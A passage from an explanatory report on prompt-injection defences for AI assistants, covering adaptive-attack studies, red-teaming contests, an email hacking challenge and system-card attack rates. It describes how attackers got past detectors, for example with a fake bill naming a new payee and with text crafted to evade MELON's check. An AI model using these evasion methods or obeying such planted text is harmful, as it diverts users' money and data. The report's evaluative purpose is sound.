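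| Done with an undo period | Reply to approved correspondents without attachments, move messages to the trash, change a meeting that involves only her, pay a known supplier the usual amount | A delay of an hour for mail and a day for payments, with notices from outside the assistant |
| Approved one by one | Write to a new address, send an attachment, invite or cancel on other people, pay a known supplier an unusual amount | A prompt that ordinary software writes from the tool call |
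| Never delegated | Add or change a payee's account, delete permanently, read login codes, change passwords, raise spending caps, alter permissions or logs | No credential for these actions, and a filter that keeps login codes away from the assistant |

The same action can belong in different rows depending on its scale. Moving one newsletter to the trash is trivial, but if the assistant moves nine thousand messages, she could overlook one she needs until the trash is automatically emptied. In a session run by Anthropic staff, Claude tried to shut down processes on about two thousand computing units at once, and auto mode stopped it. With a limit of, say, twenty messages a day, the assistant would need her approval for any larger cleanup.

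The table splits payments into three rows because the risk depends mostly on who receives the money. Once she has entered Bob's account herself, the worst a forged invoice can do is make the assistant overpay Bob, who can return the excess. She has a day to notice, and the monthly cap limits the total. Entering a new account by hand takes a few minutes, and she should confirm the account number by calling a phone number she already had, not the one on the invoice.

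Replies are harder to place. The hour's delay lets her stop a bad message if she looks, but she will not check every one, and nobody can recall a sent message. If her mailbox contains clients' medical or legal records, replies belong in the third row. That would add perhaps ten prompts a day, and she may start approving them without reading them. She might do better to have the assistant save its replies as drafts and send them herself.

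## Testing the defenses with an attacker who adapts

The user sorted her assistant's actions by possible harm because she did not know how often it would fail. Vendors and researchers publish failure rates, and many are close to zero. Most of these rates come from static attacks, a fixed list written before the defense was chosen. A real attacker can try an attack, observe the result and revise the attack. Researchers who did this broke most of the detectors and trained models they attacked. Defenses that restrict tool calls have held up better, but in fewer tests.

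### What a fixed list measures

Many of the rates quoted above come from AgentDojo, a benchmark published in 2024. Each test case combines a user's task, such as paying a bill, with an attacker's goal, such as sending himself money. The software plants the attack somewhere an outsider could write, and the assistant works through the task with simulated tools. A program then checks the simulated bank or mailbox to determine whether the assistant finished the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. The banking, chat and travel parts contain 57 user tasks and 21 attacker goals, which combine into 389 cases.

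AgentDojo can run any attack text, but researchers mostly use the text that comes with it, a blunt message that claims to be from the user and tells the assistant to do something else first. A defense can do well against this message without being secure, because a detector may have learned to recognize that kind of message or the model may already ignore it. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that the standard attack succeeded in only 0.3% of cases against Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defense. Any product built on that model would look almost perfect on this test, even if its defenses contributed nothing.

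Image-recognition researchers had already seen many defenses against doctored images withstand fixed attacks, then fail when someone adapted the attack to them. In 2020, one team broke thirteen defenses whose designers had tested them with adaptive attacks, so a weak adaptive test can also mislead.

### *The Attacker Moves Second*

In October 2025, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues published *The Attacker Moves Second*, in which they attacked twelve published defenses for language models. The team included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. In their original evaluations, most of the defenses had attack success rates near zero. The new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve.

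Two of the twelve defenses targeted jailbreaks and ten targeted prompt injection. Those ten were spotlighting and sandwiching, the trained models StruQ and Meta-SecAlign, four detectors, and Data Sentinel and MELON, which rely on a check that the attacker supposedly does not know about.

The researchers used four kinds of attacker, all of which repeat the same cycle of proposing a text, scoring the result, keeping the best attempts and revising them:

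- A gradient attack uses the model's internal numbers to calculate which changes to the text would help. The researchers found this unreliable and used it on only one defense.
- A reinforcement-learning attack trains an attacker model on its own successes and failures.
- A search attack has one language model rewrite the most promising earlier attempts and another rate the results from 1 to 10. It could query the defended system up to 800 times per scenario.
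- More than 500 people competed in an online contest for $20,000 in prizes.

The results of the search attack show how little the fixed one had measured.

| Defense | Gemini 2.5 Pro, fixed attack | Gemini 2.5 Pro, search attack | GPT-5 Mini, fixed attack | GPT-5 Mini, search attack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 0% | 75% |
| Spotlighting | 28% | 99% | 0% | 47% |
| Sandwiching | 21% | 95% | 0% | 69% |
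| Protect AI's detector | 15% | 90% | 0% | 81% |
| PIGuard | 0% | 71% | 0% | 49% |
| Prompt Guard | 26% | 94% | 0% | 75% |
| Model Armor | 28% | 90% | 0% | 56% |
| MELON | 0% | 89% | 0% | 71% |

On GPT-5 Mini, the fixed attack failed every time, even with no defense, so its results could not show whether a defense worked. The search attack succeeded in about half to four-fifths of the scenarios. Some defenses did force the attacker to make more queries. Where the search succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro, it typically needed 13 queries with no defense and 46 with PIGuard. But an automated attacker can easily send a few dozen more queries, and PIGuard cut the share of tasks the assistant completed from 74% to 39%.

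The defense MELON runs the assistant twice, once with the user's request and once with a harmless request to summarize what the tools returned. If the assistant makes the same tool call both times, the call probably came from planted text, so MELON raises an alarm. On a Llama model, a search attack that had no information about this design succeeded 76% of the time. When the researchers gave the attacker the design, it soon wrote planted instructions that told the assistant to ignore them if its task was to summarize. This kept the attacker's tool call out of the second run, so MELON had no match to detect, and the success rate rose to 95%.

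These attackers had advantages that a stranger sending an email would lack. For example, the search attack against the detectors received a confidence score after each attempt. Nasr and colleagues chose this setup because security researchers normally assume that the attacker knows the design and has ample computing power. Their success rates show that someone can break a defense, but they don't measure the chance that the next malicious email will succeed.

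As a group, people did better than the search. At least one contestant succeeded in each of the 29 scenarios that both attempted, while the search succeeded in 69%. That comparison favors the people, because up to several hundred of them attempted each scenario and the search ran only once. Three people tried all 29 scenarios. The best of them succeeded in 75%, and the search beat the other two. In late 2025, then, an automated attack was about as good as a strong contestant but missed attacks that a large group would find.

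The researchers did not test CaMeL or similar systems. CaMeL sets its plan before it reads any untrusted data, so they expected attacks to fail in most of their scenarios. They suggested testing such systems on tasks where the data has to influence the plan. Their results are strong evidence against relying on a detector or a trained model alone, but they are not evidence for or against defenses that check tool calls.

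### AutoDojo and the attacker who sees only success

AutoDojo (Ma et al., 2026) tests some of those defenses against a much more realistic attacker. He can write in one place the assistant will read, such as a hotel review or a bill. He does not know what the user will ask or which defense is running, and he learns only how many times his text succeeded. That feedback is realistic for theft, since someone who redirects payments to his own account can count the ones that arrive.

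The benchmark starts with attacks from earlier research and ranks them by success. A language model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, then uses the ranking to suggest why some attacks worked and others failed, and writes a new one. The software tries it on every user task that involves the same document and adds its score to the ranking. After six rounds, the software reports the best new attack. The attacker needs no access to the model's internal numbers and no training, only a subscription to a good language model.

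Ma and colleagues tested ten defenses on five models. Members of the team had helped develop three of the defenses (PIGuard, ROPE and DRIFT), which gives them an interest in the outcome, although their attack seriously weakened PIGuard. DRIFT plans the tool calls from the user's request and has a language model judge departures from the plan. The table shows the results for GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo, where utility is the share of tasks completed with no attack present.

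| Defense | Fixed attack | AutoDojo | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 58.6% | 52.4% | 66.7% |
| Reminder not to obey the text | 39.3% | 40.4% | 68.4% |
| Spotlighting | 51.7% | 46.8% | 59.6% |
| Prompt Guard | 54.2% | 49.4% | 63.2% |
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% | 43.9% |
| Protect AI's detector | 7.2% | 15.4% | 47.4% |
| DataFilter | 12.6% | 33.4% | 64.9% |
| Progent | 8.2% | 7.7% | 63.2% |
| DRIFT | 2.6% | 6.4% | 49.1% |
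| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 26.3% |
| ROPE | 6.4% | 4.4% | 59.6% |

In some rows, the adaptive attack did worse than the fixed one because AutoDojo is not allowed to report one of its starting texts unchanged, even if that text was the best. A real attacker could use that text as it is, so the higher of the two figures is a better guide to what such an attacker could achieve.

PIGuard blocked the fixed attack every time but let through more than a quarter of the adaptive attacks. In one case, very similar to the example assistant's work, a user asked the assistant to pay a bill stored in a file, and the attacker wanted the money sent to them instead. PIGuard cut almost all of the standard attack out of the bill, leaving nothing the assistant could act on. AutoDojo's version was written as a bill, with an amount due, a payee and a notice that the payment destination had changed. No sentence read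 like an order to an AI, so PIGuard let the whole document through, and the assistant paid the attacker and reported the bill as paid.

Nasr and colleagues broke PIGuard 71% of the time, while AutoDojo's attacker succeeded 28.0% of the time. The two figures are compatible, since Nasr and colleagues' attacker had a larger budget, received the detector's scores and could write a separate text for each task. More information does not always help, though. When Ma and colleagues gave AutoDojo's attacker PIGuard's scores and the reason for each failure, its success rate fell to 23.4%. The attacker concentrated on getting past the detector and wrote texts that the assistant was less likely to act on. Extra rounds raised the rate slightly, to 30.8% after twelve.

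#### Why open-ended requests are easier to hijack

Ma and colleagues also sorted the user tasks by how much each request left open. Some requests specify everything, such as a change of address that includes the new address. Others name the action but leave the details to a document, such as a request to pay the bill in a certain file. The most open ones, like the to-do list request discussed earlier, leave even the choice of action to the content the assistant reads.

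With PIGuard protecting GPT-4o-mini, AutoDojo succeeded in 17.3% of the fully specified cases, 31.1% of those with open details and 54.2% of those with an open action. When the user has asked for a calendar entry, a payment is out of place, so the attacker has to persuade the model to make it. But a payment listed on a page looks like part of the task if the user has asked the assistant to do whatever the page says. The attacker can write it as an ordinary item, which leaves little for a detector to recognize.

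The explanation is convincing, but there is little evidence for the most open category, because AgentDojo has only four such tasks, which produce 24 test cases. The same pattern appeared in the programming and shopping parts of AgentDyn, the benchmark with less predictable tasks. It did not appear in the part on everyday errands, apparently because the assistant read much the same material there whatever the user asked.

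Progent, DRIFT and ROPE did not show the pattern either. On AgentDojo, neither attack succeeded more than 11% of the time against any of them, whatever the type of request. For an open-ended request, Progent and DRIFT often allow only read-only tools. This blocks the attacker's payment, but it would also block a genuine payment on the same list.

#### Security against usefulness

CaMeL was the most effective defense overall. Neither attack succeeded more than 1.8% of the time on any model. But CaMeL also reduced utility the most on four of the five models. With Claude Haiku 4.5, for instance, the share of tasks completed fell from 70.2% to 40.4%.

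Progent reduced the share of tasks completed much less on AgentDojo, by at most 7 percentage points on four models and by 10.6 on DeepSeek-v4-Flash. On AgentDyn, however, it cut Gemini 2.5 Flash's share from 36.7% to 1.7%, nearly disabling the model as it had GPT-4o-mini. A buyer who had read only the AgentDojo figures would expect Progent to leave an assistant almost as useful as before, and might get one that can hardly do anything.

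The choice of models limits how far these results apply. All five are small, and GPT-4o-mini dates from 2024, so its figures are not a sound estimate for a leading model from late 2026. AutoDojo succeeded only 1.8% of the time against Claude Haiku 4.5 with no defense. In a separate run on the larger DeepSeek-v4-Pro with PIGuard, the success rate rose from 0% with the fixed attack to 8.2% with the adaptive one, and to 13.2% on the banking tasks. The gap between fixed and adaptive attacks therefore persists on a stronger model, but it may be much smaller than the GPT-4o-mini figures suggest.

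#### A second test of Progent

Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent independently, on a different model. They object that researchers have validated policy-based defenses mostly on static attacks, as researchers also did with detectors that were later broken. Progent's designers had tried some adaptive attacks on it themselves, but there is no standard adaptive test for policy-based defenses as a group.

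On AgentDojo, Progent cut the standard attacks' average success rate over three runs from 25.8% to 4.2%. The team then handwrote an attack aimed at Progent, which succeeded 2.6% of the time.

This agrees with AutoDojo's result, but it is weak evidence. The test used Qwen2.5-7B, a small, old model. The adaptive attack used a single template, and nobody tried an attack that exploits the model's internal numbers. The adaptive attack did worse than the fixed list, so it probably didn't find the defense's weak points. Narisetty and colleagues rightly conclude that the result is consistent with policies being harder to beat than detectors but does not establish it.

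### The Gray Swan contest

Automated attackers use attacks that a language model generates. To find out what people would try against the leading models of the time, Gray Swan, a company that tests AI security, ran a three-week public contest with the UK AI Security Institute, its US counterpart CAISI and several AI developers. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports the results. Competing for $40,000 in prizes, 464 people made 271,588 attempts on 13 models, and 8,648 succeeded.

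An attack usually counted as successful only if the assistant took a specified harmful action and kept any sign of it out of its answer to the user. In one scenario, a user asks for urgent emails, and the attack succeeds if text planted in a marketing message gets the assistant to mark an email about a critical deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. The user of the example assistant would learn of such an attack only when she missed the deadline.

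Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. They succeeded most often in scenarios where the assistant used tools such as email, at 4.82% on average, compared with 2.51% in programming scenarios.

Such percentages depend heavily on what the researchers count. The 8,648 successes are 3.2% of all attempts, but 12.8% of the 67,634 attempts for which participants requested a verdict. Success can also be counted by scenario. In the main rounds, at least one participant found a working attack on Claude Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios, and on Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. Someone deciding whether to trust an assistant with a particular job learns more from whether any attack succeeded on that kind of job than from an average that includes every beginner's failed attempts.

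The mix of participants matters too. In the 2025 contest, people's submissions succeeded 28.8% of the time against an undefended Gemini 2.5 Flash and 43.7% of the time when it used spotlighting. Spotlighting may have helped the attackers, but more likely different people took part or some submitted a working attack repeatedly.

The number of successful attacks rose roughly in proportion to the number of attempts. It should have leveled off if the weaknesses were few and easily exhausted, but it didn't for any model. Attacks that had beaten Claude Opus 4.5, the strongest model, succeeded between 44% and 81% of the time against each of the other models, while none of the tested attacks that had beaten the much weaker Qwen3 VL worked on Opus. A vendor who tests a product with attacks that worked on weak models will therefore overestimate its security.

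A large collection of attacks can also contain fewer methods than its size suggests, so counting different methods is more useful than counting successes. Dziemian and colleagues removed exact duplicates, but near copies remained. One participant made 63 successful attacks from a single template, telling the model it was inside a simulation and showing it a fake control panel. With small changes, the template worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reports that a larger number of attacks found by testers may be one attack repeated, and that training on more attacks left agents easier to hijack.

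Participants could read the whole conversation before the attack and knew exactly which tool call they had to trigger. An outsider would have to guess both. But participants could plant text in only one place and had only one turn, so the contest did not cover attacks that build up over several emails. Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound for single-turn attacks, which seems too strong, since a more skilled or better-funded group could succeed more often. Most of the models also ran with step-by-step reasoning switched off.

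The *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), from the developer Reflection, lists further rounds of the contest up to August 2026 and a three-week public bounty for attacks on agents together with the software that surrounds them in real products. Kahn (2026), in *AI security company Gray Swan relaunches its red teaming contest*, reports $300,000 in prizes for the relaunched arena in October. Attacks on complete products should be a better test of what a customer buys than attacks on models in prepared scenarios.

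### Six thousand emails to one assistant

The OpenClaw challenge mentioned at the start seems to suggest the opposite. In early 2026 Fernando Irarrázaval gave his test assistant an email address, a file of secrets and about 15 lines of security instructions, then invited the public to extract the secrets. The rules on the HackMyClaw site (2026) allowed attacks only by email, and the prize grew to $1,000. The assistant, which ran on Claude Opus 4.6, could send email, and the only restriction on this was an instruction to get its owner's approval first.

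In the first days of a challenge to hack an AI assistant by email, Irarrázaval (2026) counted 4,000 emails from 1,600 senders in *What happens when you put an AI agent's email on Hacker News*. *What happened after 2,000 people tried to hack my AI assistant* (Willison, 2026) reported in June that there had been about 6,000 emails and that none had worked. Google had suspended the assistant's account because of the traffic, and the model had cost about $500 to run.

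If those emails were a random sample of what attackers send, zero successes in 6,000 would put the true success rate below about 0.05% with 95% confidence. About 30 should have worked at the 0.5% success rate that contestants achieved against the slightly older Claude Opus 4.5. The newer model may be better, but several commenters in Hacker News' *HackMyClaw* pointed out that the conditions were also much harder for the attackers.

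The most important difference is that they got almost no feedback. The assistant checked its mail every few hours and normally did not reply to failed attempts. A sender could not tell whether the model had nearly complied or never received the message, so most people sent one-off attempts. Walsh, whose attack on OpenClaw's memory succeeded in April, could read the assistant's logs and revise his emails accordingly. Despite its size, the challenge was hardly an adaptive test by the standard of this section.

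The volume of attacks also made the assistant more cautious. One commenter argued that it read many emails together, so the crude attempts exposed the subtle ones. After about 500 emails, the assistant wrote in its memory that it was probably part of a security exercise, and it began to skip messages that looked like attacks. Irarrázaval had to restart it several times. The model would get no such warning from an ordinary mailbox, in which one invoice in thousands is malicious. Another commenter suspected that Gmail's spam filter had blocked many of the emails before they reached the assistant.

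The challenge also didn't measure whether the assistant was still useful. The assistant's instructions named the file it had to protect, and it had no real work that required sending information to anyone. A commenter noted that it is easy to configure an assistant to refuse so many requests that nobody can trick it. Someone who needs an assistant to send replies and make payments can't configure it that way.

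*Phishing for Lobsters* (2026) describes a Varonis test in which an OpenClaw agent forwarded mock passwords and customer data. The agent handled requests in a business mailbox, using Gemini 3.1 Pro and GPT-5.4. The email that obtained the passwords came from an outside address, was signed with the team leader's name and claimed there was an emergency. The email that obtained the customer list simply asked for it in a casual tone. Both worked even when the agent's instructions told it to verify who was asking.

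The assistant did better in two other scenarios, a gift-card scam and a malicious login request. It recognized suspicious websites but trusted an ordinary request from a supposed colleague. Varonis does not report how many times it ran each scenario, and it used different models from the challenge, so the two results cannot be compared directly. They still show that the assistant's job matters as much as the number of attacks. Irarrázaval would now let the assistant answer every email, because he thinks a patient attacker with 20 exchanges is more dangerous than 20 attempts at once.

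The 6,000 failed attempts are still good evidence that a strong model resists casual attacks by email, which are probably most of the attacks an ordinary user will receive, but they are weak evidence that it would resist an attacker who has singled her out.

### A test procedure

A company can run the following test on an assistant before relying on it. An individual usually cannot, but can ask the vendor which steps it has carried out.

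1. **Write down the attacker's goals.** For the example assistant, these could be a payment to an account that the user has not entered, the arrival of the dummy code TEAPOT-42 on the tester's server, a canceled meeting and a false note in the assistant's memory. The tester should check the bank's records and the server's log, not the assistant's own report. An automatic score also needs spot checks by a person. In one of Nasr and colleagues' experiments, the attacker model learned to raise its score by repeating a word many times, which proved nothing about the defense.

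2. **Decide what the attacker knows.** The strictest test gives him the design of the defense, a copy to practice on and a view of every tool call. A second run can give him only what an outsider would notice, such as whether the money arrived. If the assistant holds out in the second run and fails in the first, its security depends on keeping the design secret, and anyone who can buy the product can study it.

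3. **Set a budget and report it.** "No successful attacks" means little without the number of attempts, the number of revisions and the hours that skilled people spent. The search attack in the 2025 study usually stopped improving after 100 to 200 queries, so a test with ten attempts is too short. The budget should cover both an automated attacker and people, since each finds attacks that the other misses. A text that works once may fail the next time, so the tester should repeat it and report how often it works.

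4. **Measure utility alongside security.** The assistant should do its ordinary work with exactly the settings used in the attack test, once with no attack and once with planted text present. Otherwise a vendor can quote the security of a strict setting and the usefulness of a loose one. The tasks should include open-ended requests, such as "deal with whatever the accountant is asking for", because these are both the easiest to hijack and the ones that strict policies tend to block.

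5. **Test the full system.** The user will run a model together with its detector, policies, memory, approval prompts and connected accounts, and an attack may pass through any of them. The test needs dummy accounts with the same permissions as the real ones, and attacks that arrive by calendar invitation and attachment as well as by email. Some should unfold over several days. After that, the tester can switch off one defense at a time. If a single layer turns out to have stopped everything, one flaw in that layer would leave the user with no protection.

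6. **Retest after each change.** A new model, a new connector or a reworded system prompt can undo an earlier result. Attacks that worked before make a quick first check. But once the developer has trained or adjusted the system against them, they are a fixed list like any other, and the tester has to let the attacker start again.

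## Turning published attack rates into an estimate of risk

Few buyers can run such a test, so most will rely on the attack success rates in a system card, the document in which a developer reports a model's safety tests at release. For the newest models, those rates are often well below 1% per attempt. To estimate risk from such a rate, a buyer also has to know which attacks it covers, how many attempts to expect and how closely the tested system matches the product.

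### The newest figures

In September 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI both published results on a benchmark that Gray Swan built from its public contests. Gray Swan selected about 1,800 attacks that had worked on many models. The scenarios cover programming, tool use, and operating a computer through its screen. Both companies report the chance that an attacker succeeds at least once in *k* attempts.

Anthropic's system card for Claude Fable 5.1 reports an attack success rate of 0.1% for one attempt, 0.7% within 10 attempts and 1.0% within 15. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports 8.5% within 15 attempts for Astra, down from 27.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

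| Model | Success within 15 attempts | Reported by |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 1.0% | Anthropic |
| Claude Opus 5 | 4.8% | Anthropic |
| Claude Fable 5 | 6.5% | Anthropic |
| GPT-6 Astra | 8.5% | OpenAI |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 9.2% | Anthropic |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 27.0% | OpenAI |

Anthropic reports rates between 24% and 53% for most other developers' models. Fable 5.1's lead over Astra on this benchmark is probably real, because Gray Swan ran both tests, and Astra had its safeguards on while the Claude models ran without their protections against prompt injection. However, the two tests used slightly different sets of attacks (1,804 and 1,810).

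OpenAI also tested Astra with GPT-Red, the automated attacker it uses in training. Astra resisted 99.79% of indirect attacks per query, compared with 96.23% for its predecessor, so the failure rate fell about eighteenfold, from 3.77% to 0.21%. The improvement is not equal across the model family, so a buyer has to check which model a product runs on. The score in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) implies a failure rate of 2.87%, about fourteen times Astra's.

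PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* tests several newer models on long office tasks, such as analyzing a bond portfolio, using attacks based on the firm's own research. With five attempts, the attack success rate was 2.4% for Gemini 4 Carbon, 4.3% for Gemini 4 Argon, 7.6% for GPT-6 Astra, and 10.0% for both Claude Fable 5.2 and Opus 5. The margins of error are two to four percentage points, so the order of the top few means little. But these results show nothing like Fable 5.1's large lead over Astra on the Gray Swan benchmark. PromptArmor sells protection against these attacks, so it benefits from a benchmark that shows them succeeding, although it found much lower rates for Google, OpenAI and Anthropic than for most of their competitors.

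Anthropic released Fable 5.2 on November 9 (*Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2*, 2026). Its system card has a section on prompt injection, according to the contents list in Mowshowitz (2026), *Fable and Mythos 5.2*. Anyone considering Fable 5.2 should use the figures in that section rather than assume that the model matches Fable 5.1.

### One model, several rates

A model's attack rate can change a lot when only the test changes. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5, published in July, reported an attack rate of 2.0% within 15 attempts on 28 Gray Swan scenarios. In September the same model scored 4.8% on 37 scenarios. If its rate on the original 28 stayed at 2.0%, its rate on the nine new ones must have averaged about 13.5%.

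The setup also changed, so harder scenarios may not be the whole explanation. Anthropic added 670 attacks and now requires outside testers to leave its general misuse classifiers on. When one of these classifiers detects a possible cybersecurity request, the software passes the request to an older model, so some of the September results come from that model rather than the one named.

A stronger attacker made a much bigger difference. Anthropic tests programming assistants with Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan that combines search, reinforcement learning and ideas from human testers. Gray Swan trains Shade against earlier Claude models in 40 scenarios, then runs it 200 times in each of the same scenarios against the newest models. The usual version succeeded in 2.68% of attempts against Opus 5, while a new version trained for longer on more varied attacks succeeded in 90.93%.

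Anthropic fairly calls the new test "highly permissive". A real attacker rarely gets to practice on the exact task he will attack, so nobody should expect nine hijackings in ten in real use. But the lower figure reflected the first attacker's limits as much as the model's strength, and a buyer could not have known that from the figure alone.

### Surfaces and safeguards

Rates also depend on how the assistant acts on the world. On the Gray Swan benchmark, most successful attacks on Fable 5.1 came when the model operated a computer through its screen. The success rate within 15 attempts was 4.1% for this kind of computer use, 0.3% for programming and 0.0% for tool use. The gap was wider for an older model, Claude Opus 4.6. VentureBeat reports that its card, published in February, shows no successful attacks in 200 attempts in a programming environment, while 17.8% of single attempts succeeded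 in screen-based computer use.

The adaptive tests suggest that programming is the less safe surface. The table gives Anthropic's results with step-by-step reasoning switched on, first as the share of attempts that succeeded and then as the number of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded.

| Test | Opus 5, no safeguards | Opus 5, with safeguards | Fable 5.1, no safeguards | Fable 5.1, with safeguards |
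|---|---|---|---|---|
| Programming, usual attacker | 2.68% (27 of 40) | 0.39% (11 of 40) | 9.26% (31 of 40) | 2.05% (18 of 40) |
| Programming, stronger attacker | 90.93% (40 of 40) | 18.21% (40 of 40) | 56.87% (38 of 40) | 12.80% (36 of 40) |
| Computer use through the screen | 0.18% (1 of 14) | 0.18% (1 of 14) | 0.07% (2 of 14) | 0.07% (2 of 14) |
| Web browser | 2.09% (7 of 110) | 0% (0 of 110) | 2.64% (10 of 110) | 0% (0 of 110) |

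The attackers may explain part of the reversal, since Gray Swan has strengthened its attacker for programming but Anthropic reports no such upgrade for computer use. No surface has a fixed level of safety across tests.

The safeguards in the first three rows are probes that scan what the assistant reads. They cut the stronger attacker's success against Opus 5 by four-fifths, yet at least one attack still got through in every scenario. The percentage is the relevant figure for a single attempt, but the number of scenarios is more relevant if the attacker is likely to keep trying. The browser test used auto mode, which adds a classifier that checks the assistant's actions, and no attack succeeded against either model. That test was also the least adaptive of the four, because testers developed the attacks against Opus 4.7 and reused them on the newer models without revising them to get past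 auto mode.

#### When another model answers

Some of Fable 5.1's figures mostly measure Opus 4.8, the older model that takes over when the cybersecurity classifier detects a problem. In the test with the stronger programming attacker, Opus 4.8 handled about 64% of the requests, including all those where the attack succeeded. The figures imply that roughly nine in ten of the requests it handled ended in a hijacking. Fable 5.1 answered 2,826 requests itself and was not hijacked in any of them.

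The browser test showed a similar pattern. Opus 4.8 took over in 11% of 1,100 attempts, or about 120, and 20 of those attacks succeeded, a rate of around 17%. When Fable 5.1 responded, the rate was just under 1%. The two rates are not quite comparable, because the classifier determines which requests go to Opus 4.8, and those may contain the more aggressive attacks. But customers who pay for Fable 5.1 get both models, so a safeguard against help with hacking has made the product more vulnerable to these attacks. Anthropic says it is working on how its classifiers interact.

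### Repeated attempts

An attacker who fails can try again. If each attempt has the same chance *p* of success and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *k* attempts is

1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*

If each query counts as one attempt, an attacker who made 100 attempts at Astra's failure rate of 0.21% would have a 1 − 0.9979¹⁰⁰, or about 19%, chance of succeeding at least once. At its predecessor's rate of 3.77%, the chance would be 98%. The improvement is large, but 19% is still high for an assistant that can make payments.

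Real attempts are not independent, however, and an average doesn't show how they are related. Suppose a developer reports a failure rate of 0.21%. Every attempt might have that chance of working, as the formula assumes. But the developer would report the same rate if attacks always worked in one situation out of 476 and never in the others. An attacker who made 100 attempts in a single situation would then still have only a 0.21% chance of success.

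Opus 4.6's results fall between these extremes. Single attempts succeeded 17.8% of the time, so the formula predicts a 95% chance of at least one success within 15 attempts and near certainty within 200. VentureBeat reports 78.6% after 200 attempts, or 57.1% with safeguards. These percentages equal 11 and 8 out of 14, and Anthropic's later test of the same surface has 14 scenarios, so they probably count scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded. Without safeguards, all 200 attempts would then have failed in three scenarios, while attacks in others succeeded quickly.

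The formula is more accurate for a few varied attempts with a low success rate. Given the 0.4% success rate of single attempts against Opus 5, it predicts a 5.8% chance of at least one success within 15 attempts. Gray Swan measured 4.8%.

The formula can also be too optimistic, because it assumes that the attacker neither learns from failures nor reuses a text that worked. But Anthropic points out that repeated attempts raise the chance of detection. The 19% is therefore best read as a rough guide to the risk from an attacker who keeps trying different texts without feedback, not as an upper limit or a forecast.

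### What no successes can prove

If none of *n* independent attempts succeeds, the highest true success rate still reasonably compatible with that result is roughly 3/*n*. This comes from setting the chance of seeing no success, (1 − *p*)^*n*, to 5% and solving for the true rate *p*. The 0.05% limit mentioned earlier for the OpenClaw challenge is 3/6,000.

This limit holds only for attacks drawn from the same source. Suppose one email in 10,000 comes from an expert whose attacks work half the time, and all the others fail. The average success rate is then 0.005%. A challenge with 6,000 emails would end without a success about three times in four, even though half of the expert's attacks would work.

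OpenAI's tests of its dots, the always-on assistants that run on GPT-6 Astra, are much more relevant to someone who wants help with mail and bills. OpenAI had GPT-Red write emails meant to make dots reveal private information, forward mail or divert payments. In 100 runs, each with 334 harmless emails and 166 attacks, none of the 16,600 attacks succeeded. In a second test, made up of 100 series of attempts, GPT-Red revised a single email after seeing the assistant's responses and tool calls. Each new version went to an assistant that had not received the earlier ones, and none of the 2,638 attempts succeeded.

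The first result puts the success rate below 0.02% if each of the 16,600 emails counts as a separate trial. But the emails in a run all reached the same assistant, and a few crude ones may have made it suspicious of the rest, as happened in the OpenClaw challenge. A cautious reader would count the 100 runs instead, which gives a limit of 3% per run. The second test avoids this problem, but the attempts within a series were versions of one email. Counting each series as one trial also gives a limit of 3%, in this case for an attacker who makes about 26 revisions.

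The source of the attacks matters, because GPT-Red's success rate was zero but skilled people's was not. Human testers found dots resistant to hidden instructions and malicious attachments, and every attempt to send data to an outside address failed. But early testing also exposed weaknesses in how dots handled sensitive information and asked for confirmation. OpenAI changed the instructions to address these. It still acknowledges "known vulnerabilities", which it says typically took a lot of setup to exploit, along with either very permissive user requests or advanced techniques.

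### From one inbox to a million

An attacker can email a million people almost as easily as one. If a million assistants read a planted instruction and 0.1% follow it, about 1,000 people are compromised. A rate that seems negligible to each user can be worth an attacker's time, and the developer has to plan for the total number of people compromised.

The average may also be misleading, because the assistants share a model. Anthropic warns that the same email sent to a thousand inboxes compromises "every agent that summarizes it". In the extreme case, 999 texts in 1,000 fail everywhere and the remaining one works on every assistant. The average is still 1,000 victims per million inboxes, but an attacker can test the texts on their own account and send everyone the one that works. Differences between mailboxes and requests make the real pattern less extreme. Spam filters and approval prompts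 further reduce the number of victims.

The most important number for an individual user is how many attacks she receives, and no system card includes it. If one message in 100,000 is an attack, as assumed earlier, the user of the example assistant would receive one about every five and a half years. If 0.1% of attacks succeed, her chance of a hijacking in a given year is about 1 in 5,500. If a hijacking costs her the full monthly payment limit of €2,000, her expected loss is less than 40 cents a year.

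If a thief singles her out and sends 100 different attacks, each with the same independent 0.1% chance of working, the chance that at least one succeeds is 9.5% and her expected loss is €190. Her risk is about 500 times higher than before, although the assistant is the same. The euro amounts are only illustrations because the inputs are invented or borrowed from other settings, but the ratio explains why a finance director and a private person can reasonably reach different conclusions from the same system card.

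### Questions to ask about a published rate

- Does it measure direct or indirect attacks? Cross reports that GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct attacks but 97.13% of indirect ones. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) describes a similar gap for GPT-5.6.
- What is it a percentage of? The browser attacks on Opus 5 succeeded in 2.09% of attempts but in 6.4% of scenarios. A rate per query may be different again if one attack involves several queries.
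- How did the attackers develop their texts? Attacks tailored to one model tend to do worse on others. For this reason Anthropic leaves models that contestants had targeted out of its Gray Swan comparison, which makes the comparison fairer but means that every model in it faces attacks written for something else.
- Which settings did the test use? The stronger programming attacker succeeded against Claude Sonnet 5 in 19.47% of attempts when the model reasoned step by step and 40.30% when it did not. Even the testers can get this wrong. Gray Swan found that runs it had labeled "without thinking" in earlier cards had in fact used reasoning.
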